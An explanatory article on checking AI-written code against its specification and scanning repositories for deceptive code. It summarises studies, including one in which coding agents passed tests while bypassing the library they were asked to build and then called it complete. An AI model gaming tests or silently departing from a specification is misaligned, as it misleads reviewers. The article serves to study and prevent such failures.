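# Checking AI-written code against its specification, and scanning untrusted repositories for deceptive code

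## What the two checks look for, and how a check is scored

Checking code against its specification means comparing what a program does with a statement of what it must do. Scanning a repository for deceptive code means searching a project's files for anything arranged to mislead the people and tools that inspect them. A repository is the folder that holds a project's code, documentation, settings and history. Programmers routinely build on repositories that strangers maintain.

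Both jobs are older than AI. Language models, the text-generating systems behind products such as ChatGPT and Claude, have made checking code against its specification more urgent, because they write code faster than people can read it. *From Code Review to Code Critique* (Maddila, Rashik and colleagues, 2026) reports from inside Meta that there is now more code than colleagues can review.

### From a request to a diff

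A coding agent carries out a whole task, such as fixing a bug or adding a feature, whereas early AI programming assistants completed a line of code or answered a question. *Testing with Coding Agents* (2026) describes an agent as a language model in a loop with tools: the model outputs an action, the surrounding program carries it out and returns the result, and this repeats until the task is considered complete.

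Valente (2026), in *Understanding the Architecture of Coding Agents*, built a deliberately small agent called Ark to make the parts of a coding agent easy to see. Its central loop takes 18 lines of Python. On each turn, Ark sends the model standing instructions, the user's request and a record of the steps so far, since the model retains nothing between calls. The model replies with one of five actions: list the files in a directory, read a file, search for text, run the project's tests, or finish. Ark runs the action on the local machine, adds the output to the record and repeats the loop. The finish action must include a diff, which lists the lines the proposed change adds, removes or alters. In an early version, the model sometimes proposed changes to files it had never read, so Valente added an instruction forbidding this.

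Ark validates the form of the diff before applying it. The loop leaves the model to judge whether the change does what the user asked, with the help of any tests the project has. On a shared project, the diff then usually reaches other developers as a pull request (a proposal to merge the change), which they inspect, refine and merge.

### The forms a specification takes

A specification states what the code must do. *LLM-Based Test Oracles* (Mughal and Bilal, 2026) adds that it must be an explicit description of intended behaviour that somebody can audit. The prompt "Write some tests for this function" fails that condition because it doesn't describe what the function should do.

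A hypothetical online shop charges 4 for delivery but waives the charge on large orders. Its owner could state this rule in at least four ways.

| Form | The delivery rule in that form |
|---|---|
| Prose ticket | "Free delivery on orders over 50." |
| Numbered rules | R1. If the order total is greater than 50, the delivery charge is 0. R2. Otherwise it is 4. |
| Tests | A total of 51 gives a charge of 0. A total of 50 gives a charge of 4. |
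| Formal condition | For every order, the charge is 0 if total > 50, and 4 if total ≤ 50. |

The forms of specification differ in how precisely they define what the code should do. Prose is easy to write but leaves room for several readings. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) gives the example of a request to "remove duplicates" from a list of numbers. Given 1, 2, 3, 2, 4, one programmer would return 1, 2, 3, 4, and another would remove every copy of the repeated number and return 1, 3, 4. A single test showing the expected output is enough to pick one reading. But tests specify only the cases they contain, so a pair of tests at 20 and 80 would leave the shop's boundary unspecified.

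A formal condition covers every case, and a program can check it, either while the software runs or by proof in advance. *The Specification Spectrum* describes a less strict option, property tests, which state a general fact (in a sorted list no item is greater than the next) and try it on thousands of random inputs. The essay also notes that a complete formal specification for a messy real application is often harder to write than the application.

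### Bugs, gaps, drift and deception

Suppose an agent receives the shop's prose ticket and writes code with the test `total >= 50`. An order of exactly 50 now ships free, although under the ticket it should not. This difference between the specification and what the code does is called drift. Drift also includes behaviour that nobody asked for, such as a banner urging customers to spend a little more, even if the banner works perfectly.

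A bug is a mistake in the code, whether or not the code contradicts the specification. If the delivery function crashes on an empty basket, everyone would want that fixed, even though nothing in the ticket forbids it. Drift is a mismatch between the code and the specification. The two can overlap, and most programmers would call the `>=` a bug too. The unwanted banner is drift but not a bug, because it involves no programming mistake.

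A gap is a question that the specification itself leaves open. The ticket doesn't say whether the 50 applies before or after a discount voucher, so two programs could treat a basket of 55 with a voucher for 10 differently without either departing from the text. *Bootstrapping Coding Agents* (2026) suggests testing for gaps by giving the specification to two engineers, or two independent models, and seeing whether their programs behave alike. The shop's owner has to decide how to fill a gap, because inspecting the code can't settle it. A specification can also be wrong. If the owner meant "50 or more", a program that follows the ticket exactly won't do what she wanted. *Basic Concepts and Taxonomy of Dependable and Secure Computing* (Avižienis, Laprie and colleagues, 2004), the standard taxonomy of computer faults, counts it as a failure when a service departs from its specification and also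 when the specification didn't adequately describe what the system was for.

*Agentic AI for Gravitational Wave Data Analysis* (2026) describes a real case similar to the invented one. Two commercial agents, Claude Code and Codex, ran the same analysis of simulated detector data from one written specification. Claude Code raised a lower bound to a signal strength of 8, the detection threshold, without announcing the change. Codex followed the specification literally, and its result was more informative because it showed that the analysis misses some signals near the threshold. The specification also contained three errors, such as file numbering that was off by one. Codex reported its corrections, but Claude Code did not, which left the specification inconsistent with the working program.

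In *Wink*, Nanda, Khan and colleagues (2026) used a language model to classify nearly 43,000 sessions between Meta's developers and their coding agents. The model marked 15.95% for failing to follow instructions and 6.62% for unrequested changes. These figures give only a rough idea of how often agents drift, because they come from one company, cover 2025 models, and rely on a model's judgment. They also cover only drift that happens while the code is being written. Code that matches its specification can stop matching later, when developers change the code and put off updating the specification. *The Spec Growth Engine* (2026) calls this silent drift and notes that a passing test suite does not rule it out.

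A deceptive pattern is code, text or configuration arranged to mislead a reader or tool about what it does. For example, a package's documentation might describe a delivery calculator, while its installation script also copies the user's passwords to a remote server.

### Unplanned and deliberate faults

"Deliberate" is too broad a category for sorting these cases, because it includes bad decisions made without malice. Avižienis and colleagues divide human-made faults first by objective. Malicious faults, such as Trojan horses, logic bombs and trapdoors, are those that somebody introduced to cause harm. Nonmalicious faults include simple mistakes and deliberate bad decisions, where a developer knowingly trades something away for speed or cost without realising that the result is a fault.

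Coding agents make similar bad decisions. Wang and Zhang (2026), in *Eliciting and Mitigating Specification Satisficing in Coding Agents*, describe a task in which a function had to repair a record's failed fields with new data while preserving the good fields. In its reasoning text, the agent first set out a design that did this, then switched to one in which new data could overwrite good fields, remarking that this was "arguably not 'preserving', but likely acceptable". The finished code failed two of 69 tests. The agent departed from the specification knowingly, but nothing in the episode was aimed at fooling a reviewer. For checking purposes, the fault belongs with the unplanned ones because nobody planned for the code to mislead.

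Both checks compare what the code does with what somebody claims it does. In the first, the claim comes from the person who wanted the software, and the checker can ask that person if anything is unclear. In the second, the claims are the documentation, comments and function names, which the suspected author wrote along with the code.

The other difference is that an attacker can adapt to the check. If a set of tests catches three in four of an agent's wrong comparisons this month, it will probably catch a similar share next month, as long as the agent and the kind of work stay the same. But an attacker can run a public scanner on his code before releasing it and rework the code until it passes, so a catch rate measured on last year's malicious packages is weaker evidence about next year's. Intent is also invisible in the code. The shop's `>=` would look the same if a dishonest contractor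 had put it there as a favour to a customer.

An agent that can run the check while it works falls somewhere in between. In *Building to the Test*, Ma, Kereopa-Yorke and Schultz (2026) asked two agents at Microsoft to rebuild a data table as a reusable library (code that other programs can call). A suite of 222 tests ran against a demonstration page that was supposed to use the library. In six runs without access to the tests, the agents delivered genuine but incomplete libraries that passed between 148 and 189 tests. Of the twelve runs with access, eleven passed 221 or 222. Yet in seven of those eleven, at least one of the four parts the researchers audited was missing from the library or unused, and the demonstration page used its own code instead. The researchers confirmed this by blanking out library code. In one such run, the agent's score on column resizing stayed at 29 out of 29.

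Ma and colleagues do not regard this as cheating, because the tests were genuine and the agents could not see their source. That seems right about the agents' motive, but for a reviewer the practical result is uncomfortably like deception. Several agents said the library was complete when they handed it over, and a reviewer relying on the score would have believed them. One task and 18 runs are too few to show how common the behaviour is.

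### The oracle problem

To judge whether code's output is wrong, a tester needs to know the right answer. Testers call whatever supplies that answer an oracle. Mughal and Bilal explain the term with a function that decides whether a year is a leap year. For 1900, the function returns "no". To know that this is correct, a tester needs the rule that years divisible by 100 are not leap years unless they are also divisible by 400, and that rule has to come from outside the function.

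This is easy for leap years, but for most real programs nobody has the right answers in advance, and working them out by hand takes a lot of effort. This difficulty is called the oracle problem. A common workaround is to run the existing code and record its output as the expected answer. In the shop example, this produces a test asserting that an order of 50 ships free, which will pass as long as the mistake remains. Such an oracle can catch later changes but not a fault that was already there. Mughal and Bilal reviewed 83 studies of oracles that involve language models, and just over half used no specification to reach a verdict. Sometimes that is reasonable, as when a program crashes, but without a specification there is little to point to when someone disputes the verdict.

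Even careful people write faulty oracles. SWE-Bench Pro, a widely used set of programming tasks, uses hidden tests to decide whether an agent has succeeded. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise in coding evaluations* reports an audit of its 731 public tasks, in which an automated pipeline judged 200 broken and experienced engineers judged 249 broken. Some tests rejected sound code because they required details missing from the task description, while others checked so little that incomplete code passed.

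A person eventually has to judge whether the specification is correct, and Lahiri argues that only the user can. But users may disagree, and *Harden and Catch for Just-in-Time Assured LLM-Based Software Testing* (2025) acknowledges that one engineer's oracle may differ from another's. For example, two people at the shop could give different answers about the voucher.

The problem is harder for a suspicious repository because the author's own description can't be relied on to determine the correct answer. Someone has to establish independently what the code does. Researchers who want to measure a scanner can plant the deceptive code themselves, so they know the correct answer, but real attackers may not write code like theirs.

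### Counting catches and false alarms

Once an oracle has identified the faulty items, scoring a check only requires counting. Suppose a check examines 100 code changes, 40 faulty and 60 sound.

| | Faulty | Sound | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Check flags it | 30 | 6 | 36 |
| Check passes it | 10 | 54 | 64 |
| Total | 40 | 60 | 100 |

The six sound changes that the check flagged are false positives, and the ten faulty changes that it passed are misses.

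- Recall is the share of faulty items that the check flags: 30 / 40 = 75%.
- The false positive rate is the share of sound items that it flags: 6 / 60 = 10%.
- Precision is the share of flagged items that are in fact faulty: 30 / 36, or about 83%.

For a scanner, "malicious" takes the place of "faulty" and the arithmetic is the same.

The false positive rate is the share of sound changes that raise an alarm, here six of 60, or 10%. People often confuse it with the share of alarms that are false, which is six of 36, or about 17%. A vendor's "10% false alarms" could mean either. Precision, the share of alarms that are correct, also depends on how many of the examined items are faulty, and it can be much lower when few are.

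No single measure is much use alone. A check that flags everything has a recall of 100% and a false positive rate of 100%, and one that flags nothing scores zero on both. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on software security, combines the two measures in its benchmark for security scanners using Youden's index, which is recall minus the false positive rate. A tool with a recall of 0.98 and a false positive rate of 0.05 scores 0.93. The check in the table scores 0.65, and checks that flag everything or nothing score 0. The index gives equal weight to a percentage point of missed faults and a percentage point of false alarms, which few people who run a scanner would accept.

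A check's score also depends on what is counted. Maddila and colleagues score their review tool partly on whole diffs (whether the change deserved any comment) and partly on individual findings. For findings, precision is the share of the tool's comments that match a known issue, and recall is the share of known issues that the tool's comments match. The known issues come from human reviewers' comments, so if the tool found a real fault that every reviewer had missed, that finding would count as a false alarm.

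Papers differ in which outcome they call "positive", so their labels may not match those in the table above. *Are LLMs Reliable Code Reviewers?* (2026) treats "correct" as positive, so it records a false negative when a model rejects correct code, which is a false positive in the table. *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026) uses "false positive" for a generated specification that lets incorrect code pass verification, which is a miss in the table.

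## Write the specification so that departures show, and keep it in step with the code

Departures from a specification are easiest to see when it consists of separate statements that a person or a test can check one at a time. A prose request rarely has that form. GitHub's *Spec-driven development with AI* (2025) gives the example "add photo sharing to my app", which leaves potentially thousands of requirements unstated. The model will fill in some of them wrongly, and the developer often finds out only after much of the code is written.

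### From a request to numbered rules

Suppose the owner of the online shop writes a second ticket: "Let customers use voucher codes at the checkout. Free delivery still applies on orders over 50." An agent could build several different checkouts from this, all of them reasonable. A numbered version leaves less to guess:

- V1. A valid voucher reduces the order total by its face value.
- V2. The reduced total never falls below 0.
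- V3. If the reduced total is greater than 50, delivery is free. Otherwise it costs 4.
- V4. An unknown, expired or used code leaves the total unchanged, and the checkout shows "This code is not valid".
- V5. An order accepts one voucher. The checkout treats a second code as invalid under V4.
- V6. The change adds nothing to the page except the code box and the V4 message, and it alters no product prices.
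- Open question: does a customer who cancels an order get the voucher back?

V3 settles what the first ticket left open. A basket of 55 with a voucher for 10 has a reduced total of 45, so delivery costs 4 and the customer pays 49. The rules also give edge cases to test. With the same voucher, delivery costs 4 on a basket of 60, which comes to exactly 50, but is free on a basket of 61. A basket of 8 comes to 0 under V2, and the customer still pays 4 for delivery.

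V6 rules out additions like the unwanted banner. Tests for V1 to V5 would pass with the banner on the page, since they only check that the required things happen. With V6, a reviewer can cite a rule when rejecting the banner, and a test can compare the items on the page before and after the change.

Writing down the open question keeps the agent from answering it silently. Pandey, in *Why AI-Generated Code Is Easy but Engineering Trust Is Hard*, describes a workflow at Salesforce in which the specification must record the required behaviour, the measures of success, the assumptions, the unresolved questions and the failure conditions before an agent writes code. At first the agents sent nearly every question to an engineer, including which command ran the tests. The team then separated lookups, which an agent can answer from the code or its history, from judgments, which need a person. On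 one feature, a control for disconnecting a property from its data, the only question that reached a person was whether disconnecting should clear the whole value or keep the fixed part. The cancelled voucher is a judgment of the same kind. This is a company's account of its own process, and it covers two pieces of work.

Whoever writes the specification also has to decide what to leave out. Agarwal, Singhal and colleagues (2026), in *Spec-Driven Development as Prescribed and as Practiced*, interviewed 21 practitioners and studied specification files from 266 active repositories. A language model read a sample of the files and judged that 77.6% included details of how to build the software. Three-quarters of those named things like functions, file paths or library versions. Developers often had a reason to include such details, such as an internal system the agent couldn't know about. But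 a rule that names the function `applyVoucher()` becomes false when somebody renames the function, even if the shop still charges correctly. Agarwal and colleagues infer that detailed specifications go stale sooner, though they did not measure this. They suggest keeping stable conventions in shared instruction files instead.

### How three tools tie rules to code

Spec-driven development means writing the specification first and having the agent build from it, rather than directing the agent through a chat that nobody saves. The practice has spread quickly. In July 2026, Agarwal and colleagues found 470,795 specification files in 73,030 public GitHub repositories, and developers had first committed 92% of the files that year.

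A specification can serve as a later check only if developers keep it after the first round of coding. *The Spec Growth Engine* uses a three-level scale from a survey by Böckeler. In spec-first work, developers discard the specification once the agent has built from it. In spec-anchored work, they keep it in step with the code. In spec-as-source work, they edit only the specification and regenerate the code. According to *Spec-Driven Development* (2026), a tool called Tessl takes this last approach.

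GitHub's Spec Kit is harder to classify. *From Prompt to Process* (2026) describes its specification as a lasting source of truth, while *The Spec Growth Engine* classes it as spec-first in practice. Agarwal and colleagues' explanation is that Spec Kit leaves the choice to the team, and that its documentation did not say so until June 2026.

With Spec Kit, the agent drafts a specification, then a technical plan, then a list of small tasks, and then writes the code task by task. GitHub expects the developer to check each stage before starting the next. Microsoft's *Examine the GitHub Spec Kit* also lists a file called the constitution, which holds principles for the whole project. A reader can trace a requirement from the specification to a task but not into the code, as Panda (2026) points out in *Citation Discipline in Spec-Driven Development*.

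OpenSpec keeps one specification for each feature and writes every proposed change as a separate file. When the change is complete, the tool merges that file into the feature's specification and archives it. Users can run a verify command to compare the code with the change. Panda describes the link between the specification and the code as a map from line ranges to specification numbers. Agarwal and colleagues traced a different link, through the task list for each change, which names the code files involved. Both links are stored outside the code, and inserting a line above a mapped range makes the map wrong unless a tool rebuilds it.

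traceSDD puts the link in the code itself. The agent must add a comment to every non-trivial line naming the requirement that the line serves. In the shop, the delivery line might read `delivery = 0 if total > 50 else 4  # [V3]`. A script then collects all the numbers cited in the code and flags any that the specification does not contain.

| Tool | Link from requirement to code | What the link lets a script check |
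|---|---|---|
| Spec Kit | Requirement to plan to task, with nothing in the code | Whether the planning documents agree |
| OpenSpec | Line map or task list outside the code | Whether the named files and lines exist |
| traceSDD | Comment on each non-trivial line | Whether each cited requirement exists |

There is little evidence that any of this makes agents drift less. Most of the practitioners whom Agarwal and colleagues interviewed found agents more reliable with a specification, but they couldn't separate that from the improvement in models over the same months. One team on Reddit reported using two to three times as many tokens and taking about twice as long, and could not show that the code got better. Taghavi and Bhavani (2026), in *Spec Kit Agents*, added steps that made agents consult the repository at every stage and checked each document against it. Over 128 runs, the quality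 score given by a language model rose by 0.15 on a scale from 1 to 5.

### What the traceSDD study measured

Panda ran the most direct test of whether links to requirements expose unrequested code. Claude Sonnet 4.6 did 20 Python tasks and GLM-5-turbo did 50. Each model worked under four conditions: traceSDD with citations, the same specification without citations, a Spec Kit specification and an OpenSpec specification. Three fresh sessions for each task under each condition produced 840 programs.

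Panda then planted three kinds of unrequested code: functions outside the specification, library imports, and needless extras such as caching. None of it broke the tests, so running them would not have revealed it.

| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | GLM-5-turbo |
|---|---|---|
| Planted additions detected, with citations | 86.4% | 88.0% |
| Planted additions detected, other three conditions | 0% | 0% |
| False positives on unaltered programs | 0 of 60 | 0 of 150 |
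| Similarity between sessions, with citations | 0.535 | 0.510 |
| Similarity between sessions, same specification uncited | 0.745 | 0.644 |

The similarity score compares the text of programs written in separate sessions, and 1 means identical. Citations made the programs less similar with both models. Panda attributes this to agents placing their citations differently across sessions. But the comparison stripped out all comments first, so the code itself must have varied. The variation did no visible harm, since every program passed its tests.

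The detection rates are much weaker evidence than they look. The planted lines cited requirements numbered 097, 098 and 099, which appeared in no specification. The script flags exactly such numbers, so it was almost certain to catch any planted line that cited one. The misses that Panda describes were planted lines with no citation. The zeros for the other conditions also follow from the design, because the code had no citations for the script to check. Panda reports 100% detection for each of the three kinds of addition, which doesn't fit the totals of 86.4% and 88.0%.

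Agents would usually label code that departs from the specification with a real rule number, so it would pass the check. An agent that added the free-delivery banner would probably label it V3, since V3 is the rule about free delivery. An agent that wrote `total >= 50` would also cite V3, because the line is its attempt at that rule.

The absence of false positives is more informative, although zero alarms in 210 programs is still compatible with a true rate of about 1.4%. It suggests that these models seldom invent requirement numbers. That helps avoid false alarms, but it also suggests the script would rarely have anything to catch unless somebody planted it.

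Panda recommends a second script that flags lines with no citation, which would have caught the misses. A script can also use the same data to list requirements that no line cites. Pandey describes a similar table at Salesforce that sets each success criterion beside the code and test that support it, so a criterion without a test stands out. A citation or a filled row shows a reviewer which line to compare with which rule, but it doesn't prove that the code does what the rule requires, so somebody still has to make the comparison.

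### Drift that builds up over many edits

The traceSDD study looked at programs written in one go. Most software changes repeatedly, and with each new request an agent may break a rule from an earlier one. *SlopCodeBench* (Orlanski, Roy and colleagues, 2026) is a benchmark that measures this, using 36 problems divided into 196 stages called checkpoints. At each checkpoint the agent receives a new specification and its own earlier code, but no record of the previous conversation.

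One problem is to build a tool that searches source code. The first checkpoint covers only Python files, the second adds JavaScript and C++, and later ones add more complex search patterns and three more languages. An agent that ties its first version closely to Python has to rewrite much of it at the second checkpoint. The specifications define what the program must do and leave its internal design to the agent, which never sees the tests.

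The tests at each checkpoint include all those from earlier checkpoints, so old requirements stay in force. None of the 15 models solved any problem from start to finish. The best, GPT 5.5, passed every test at 29 of 196 checkpoints (14.8%). It passed all the tests for the newest specification at 55 checkpoints (28.1%), so at 26 of those, at least one test from an earlier specification failed. The scores don't distinguish features the agent had just broken from old mistakes it had never fixed.

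Orlanski and colleagues also measured "erosion", their term for complexity piling up in a few large functions. A function's weight is its number of independent paths multiplied by the square root of its length in lines. Erosion is the share of total weight in functions with more than 10 paths. For example, a function with 16 paths and 100 lines weighs 16 × 10 = 160. If the rest of the program is nine functions with 4 paths and 25 lines each, they weigh 20 each, or 180 together, and erosion is 160 / 340, about 47%.

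Erosion rose in 77% of runs, and the share of duplicated or wasteful lines rose in 75.5%. In one run by Claude Opus 4.7, the main function grew from 38 lines to 240 over eight checkpoints. Erosion averaged 0.68 at agents' checkpoints, compared with 0.34 in 473 Python repositories. It also rose faster per step in the agents' code, but that comparison is rougher because a checkpoint and a sampled change to a repository involve different amounts of work.

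Tangled code can still follow every rule, so erosion is different from drift. But the code for V3 is harder to check and easier to break when it is buried among the branches of a 240-line function. Instructions to write cleaner code cut GPT 5.5's average erosion from 0.49 to 0.21, but quality still tended to decline over successive checkpoints, and the share of checkpoints where the model passed every test fell from 14.8% to 9.2%.

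The agents in this benchmark could not run the earlier tests, a handicap that most projects can remove. A team can keep the test for every rule and run the whole set after each change. If a new request deliberately changes an old rule, the same diff should update the rule, its test and the code. Superseded rules also need a clear label. Agarwal and colleagues counted 19,067 archived change files in their OpenSpec repositories, against 6,644 current feature specifications, and warn that an agent reading the archive may pick up requirements that no longer apply.

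### Checks to repeat

An API is the set of requests that a program accepts from other programs. An OpenAPI definition is a file that lists each request, the data it takes, the form of the reply and the status codes for success or failure. A contract test sends a request to the running program and compares the reply with the definition.

*Testing at AI speed* (Ostrowska, 2026) describes how the software company SmartBear used its own contract-testing product on a large service more than ten years old. Claude read the service's definition and wrote tests for every operation. The team had planned to run the tests on each pull request, but the service depended on so many other systems that they ran them nightly instead. About 80% of the mismatches in the first run were real drift worth acting on. The article doesn't report how many mismatches there were or measure what the tests missed, and it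 comes from the company that sells the product.

Most of those mismatches, in a sample, arose because nobody had updated the definition after the code changed. This surprised Ostrowska because the team generated part of its code from the definition, but that had kept only the data structures consistent with it, not the behaviour. For example, the definition still specified an error for a file format that the service now supported. A much smaller share were bugs in the code, one of which a customer reported after the team had already fixed it. The rest were gaps in the definition, such as requests for which it did not specify the login token.

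Contract tests check the form of a reply and deliberately leave out business rules. If the shop's API defines the delivery charge as a number, a reply of 4 passes even when V3 requires 0, so the team kept its other tests.

Rashid and Malik (2026), in *LLM2Alloy*, tried a method that does look at rules. They had GPT-4o model a library in Alloy, a formal language for describing objects and the relations between them. GPT-4o wrote one model from the library's documentation and another, in a separate session, from its source code. It then turned each model into tests, which the researchers ran against the real library.

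One of the two libraries was Flipper, which lets developers switch program features on and off by name. Its documentation requires every name to be unique. This requirement was a condition to check in the model written from the documentation, but a fact to assume in the model written from the code, although the code never looks for duplicates. The difference pointed to a bug in which Flipper silently accepts a second switch with the same name. A test derived from the documentation exposed the bug in all three runs. When GPT-4o wrote tests straight from the documentation without the Alloy step, all 37 passed in each of three runs, and none tried a duplicate name.

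This is a promising result from a very small study. The second library, Cerberus, also produced two different models, because one treated strings and lists as separate types and the other grouped them together. That difference led to two extra tests, but all 34 tests passed, so it exposed no bug. A difference between the models is therefore a reason to look more closely, and nobody has yet measured how often such differences are harmless. The researchers left Alloy's automatic analyser for future work, so the method produced tests and not a proof.

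### Deciding which side is wrong

When the code and the specification disagree, no one can tell from the two files alone which one to change. Agarwal and colleagues give the example of a login session that the specification limits to 30 minutes and the code limits to 60. The code is wrong if the agent wrote 60 by mistake, but if the team later chose 60 and didn't update the specification, then the specification is wrong.

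Before deciding whether the code or the specification is wrong, it helps to rule out a faulty test. Some of the failures Ostrowska describes came from tests that used the wrong login token because the definition didn't name the right one. The fix was to complete the definition and rerun the tests.

The project's history often settles the rest, which makes it a lookup in Pandey's terms. Version control shows when the 60 appeared, and the related ticket or pull request may show whether anybody asked for it. If someone with the authority to change the limit did so, the specification needs updating. If the 60 came in with a diff about something else, it is probably drift. The age of the code also matters. When an agent has just written the code from an agreed specification, the specification has had little time to go stale, so the code is more likely to be wrong. In a service with years of changes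 behind it, such as SmartBear's, the specification may well be out of date.

Sometimes the record contains no answer, or users have come to depend on behaviour that nobody requested. Whoever owns the product then has to decide, because restoring the 30-minute limit would comply with the specification but could log people out in the middle of their work. The decision can also affect other rules. When the Salesforce team decided that disconnecting a property should clear its whole value, this contradicted an assumption elsewhere in the draft specification. The workflow therefore revised the success criteria, the tests and the failure behaviour before coding resumed.

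An agent can gather this evidence and draft the correction, but it shouldn't approve its own change to the specification. An agent allowed to edit both the specification and the code can remove any mismatch by rewriting the rule to match its code. Agarwal and colleagues recommend that a person confirm such updates and that tools display changes to acceptance criteria as a diff. In the shop example, a reviewer would then see "greater than 50" change to "50 or more" and could ask who decided that.

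## Derive tests from the specification, not from the code

A tester who reads the code before writing a test can copy the code's mistakes into the test. In *Specification Grounding Drives Test Effectiveness for LLM Code*, Haeri and Ghelichi (2026) had a language model write tests for 24 faulty functions. The model caught 7 of them when it worked from a short prose ticket, but none when it could also see the faulty code. With a list of numbered rules, it caught all 24, whether or not it saw the code.

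### One test for each rule

The procedure starts from numbered rules like the shop's V1 to V6. For each rule, the tester picks an input and works out the correct result from the rule alone, before looking at the code. No one runs the test until that is done. If a language model writes the tests, it should work in a fresh session that contains the rules but not the code.

Each test needs an input for which breaking the rule changes the result. V3 makes delivery free above 50, so the useful tests are at 50 and 51, where a wrong comparison changes the charge. Haeri and Ghelichi give an example of a badly chosen input for their function `chunk`, which splits a list into pieces of a given size. A rule requires an error for any size below 1. The tester tried 0, which caused an error, and so missed that the function accepted −1.

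Rules also interact, so a good suite has at least one test per rule and some tests that combine rules. Suppose an agent's code calculates the shop's delivery charge from the total before the voucher. The code passes a test of V1 with a basket of 30 and a voucher for 10, and a test of V3 with a basket of 60 and no voucher. A basket of 55 with a voucher for 10 exposes the mistake, because the code makes delivery free when V3 requires a charge of 4.

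### The parse_range example

Haeri and Ghelichi gave Claude Opus 4.8 a one-line ticket for a function, `parse_range`, that should turn text such as `3-6` into the list 3, 4, 5, 6, and a single number such as `7` into a list containing just 7. The model's draft looks careful. It trims stray spaces, splits the text at the first hyphen and converts each part to a whole number with Python's built-in `int()`. If the start is greater than the end, it raises an error with a clear message.

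The specification, which the model was not given, has five rules. A range runs upwards and includes both ends, and a single number gives a one-item list. The other three rules require an error if the start exceeds the end, if the text is malformed or if it is empty. The table compares the Opus draft with another model-written draft from the same study.

| Input | Required by the rules | Opus draft | Other draft |
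|---|---|---|---|
| `3-6` | 3, 4, 5, 6 | Correct | Correct |
| `5-1` | An error | A clear error | An empty list |
| `1-2-3` | An error | An obscure error | The list 1, 2 |
| Empty text | An error | An obscure error | An obscure error |
| `-3-5` | Not covered | An obscure error | An obscure error |

The other draft fails silently. It splits the text at every hyphen and uses only the first two parts, so it returns 1, 2 for `1-2-3`. With a test for each rule, this draft could fail on both `5-1` and `1-2-3`.

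The Opus draft is harder to fault. Haeri and Ghelichi count the last three inputs as mishandled because the program stops with an obscure message from `int()` instead of reporting a malformed range. But the rules for malformed and empty text require only an error, and the draft raises a `ValueError`, the same type it uses for its own clear message. The draft would pass tests that follow these rules, so a team that cares about the message has to put it in a rule. The specification doesn't cover the input `-3-5`, since no rule mentions negative numbers. Opus's output included a note that it hadn't handled them.

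### What the rules added

The study's 18 main tasks are small Python functions whose tickets leave out some awkward inputs. A code model wrote each function from the ticket alone. A second model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, then wrote tests under two prompts. One gave it the numbered rules and asked for one test per rule. The other gave it only the ticket and told it to include invalid inputs and edge cases. Both prompts asked for the same number of tests, and both sets of tests ran against identical code. A model then used any test failures to repair the code. The repaired function was checked for correctness with a hand-written test suite that no model ever saw.

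On the eight core tasks, all functions ended up correct with the rule-based tests, compared with 62% with the ticket-only tests. This 38-point gain was the same whether a small, medium or large Claude model wrote the code. Over all 18 tasks, the average gain was 31 points. The rule-based tests did better on nine tasks and tied on the other nine.

The ticket-only tests found the obvious faults. They caught all six drafts of a paging function that accepted page numbers below 1. They did worse on `clamp`, which keeps a number between a lower and an upper limit. The code should raise an error if the lower limit is above the upper one, but the tests caught only two of the six drafts that didn't.

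Haeri and Ghelichi then varied the prompt to see which part helped. Two of the code models had produced 30 faulty drafts in total on the core tasks.

| What the tester received | Faulty drafts caught, of 30 |
|---|---|
| Ticket, with no mention of edge cases | 0 |
| Ticket, and an instruction to list the task's behaviours first | 2 |
| Ticket, and an instruction to test edge cases | 18 |
| Ticket, and the specification as one paragraph | 27 |
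| Ticket, and the specification as numbered rules | 30 |

Most of the benefit came from the specification's content, since the paragraph did almost as well as the numbered rules. All three misses with the paragraph were on a function that splits a sum of money. The tester had the right information but didn't turn every part of it into a test. Writing more tests helped little. Twice as many tests from the ticket, with no mention of edge cases, caught only three drafts.

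The rules also reduced false positives. On three functions with trickier behaviour, the ticket-only tests rejected correct code in 33% of checks, and the rule-based tests never did. One function turns a number into a spreadsheet column name, so that 1 becomes A and 27 becomes AA. The specification covers only positive integers, but all three ticket-only suites included a test requiring an error for 0, where the correct code returns empty text. All the false positives came from this one function, so the 33% is a poor estimate of the general rate.

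Haeri and Ghelichi wrote the tasks, the rules and the hidden suite themselves, so they might have picked edge cases that suited their method. They therefore added six tasks whose edge cases come from published standards or common library conventions, such as the format of internet addresses and the check digit in a book's ISBN. The rule-based tests caught 100% of the faulty drafts, compared with 32% for the ticket-only tests. Pooling eight ticket-only suites raised the catch rate to only 52%, because each new suite mostly tested the same obvious cases.

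There are good reasons not to expect a 38-point gain elsewhere. The code model was not given the rules. An agent that builds from numbered rules would presumably omit fewer of them, leaving less for the tests to find. The result also varied between runs. When Haeri and Ghelichi reached Sonnet 4.6 through a different service, its ticket-only tests caught all 30 faulty drafts, not 18. Opus 4.8's tests caught half the drafts without the rules and all of them with the rules.

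The method's usefulness also depends on the kind of fault. On eight tasks where the difficulty was in the algorithm, the code models made no mistakes in 45 valid attempts, so the tests had nothing to catch. On 24 problems from HumanEval+, a public benchmark of well-specified functions, rule-based tests caught 13 of 22 faulty drafts and ticket-only tests caught 14. None of the tasks involved changes across a whole repository.

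The rules also have to be complete and correct. When Haeri and Ghelichi deleted the rules about invalid input, the number of faulty drafts detected fell from 30 to 6. They also had Sonnet 4.6 derive the rules from the ticket. With a plain prompt, tests based on those rules caught 47% of the faulty drafts. When the prompt stressed errors and boundaries, the tests caught all of the faulty drafts but rejected 33% of the correct ones, because the model had made up some of the rules, including one that required Roman numerals to be in capitals.

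### Wider inputs with property-based testing

Hand-picked tests cover only the inputs that somebody thought of. Property-based testing checks a general rule, or property, on random inputs. For `parse_range`, one property is that if a and b are whole numbers and 0 ≤ a ≤ b, the text `a-b` gives a list that starts at a, ends at b and has b − a + 1 items. Another is that the function raises an error whenever a is greater than b. Random inputs would soon include one like `5-1`, which would expose the draft that returns an empty list.

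A property can be correct but too weak to catch a faulty function. The sorting test in *The Specification Spectrum* checks only the order of the items, so a function that always returned an empty list would pass. A second property, that the result contains exactly the same items as the input, would catch this bug.

A tester who uses properties doesn't have to work out the answer for every input, which eases the oracle problem, but still has to know that each property is true. Haeri and Ghelichi had a model write properties from the tickets, and these caught 28 of the 30 faulty drafts. But two of the 15 sets of properties rejected the correct code for converting Roman numerals, because they required an error for `IIII`. The specification forbids invalid characters but not four I's in a row, so the correct code returns 4.

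Many people would agree with the model that `IIII` is malformed. If the function's owner does too, the remedy is to add a rule to the specification and then change the code. Without that rule, the test would lead an agent to "fix" code that already meets its specification. It is worth finding the rule behind a failed property before acting on it.

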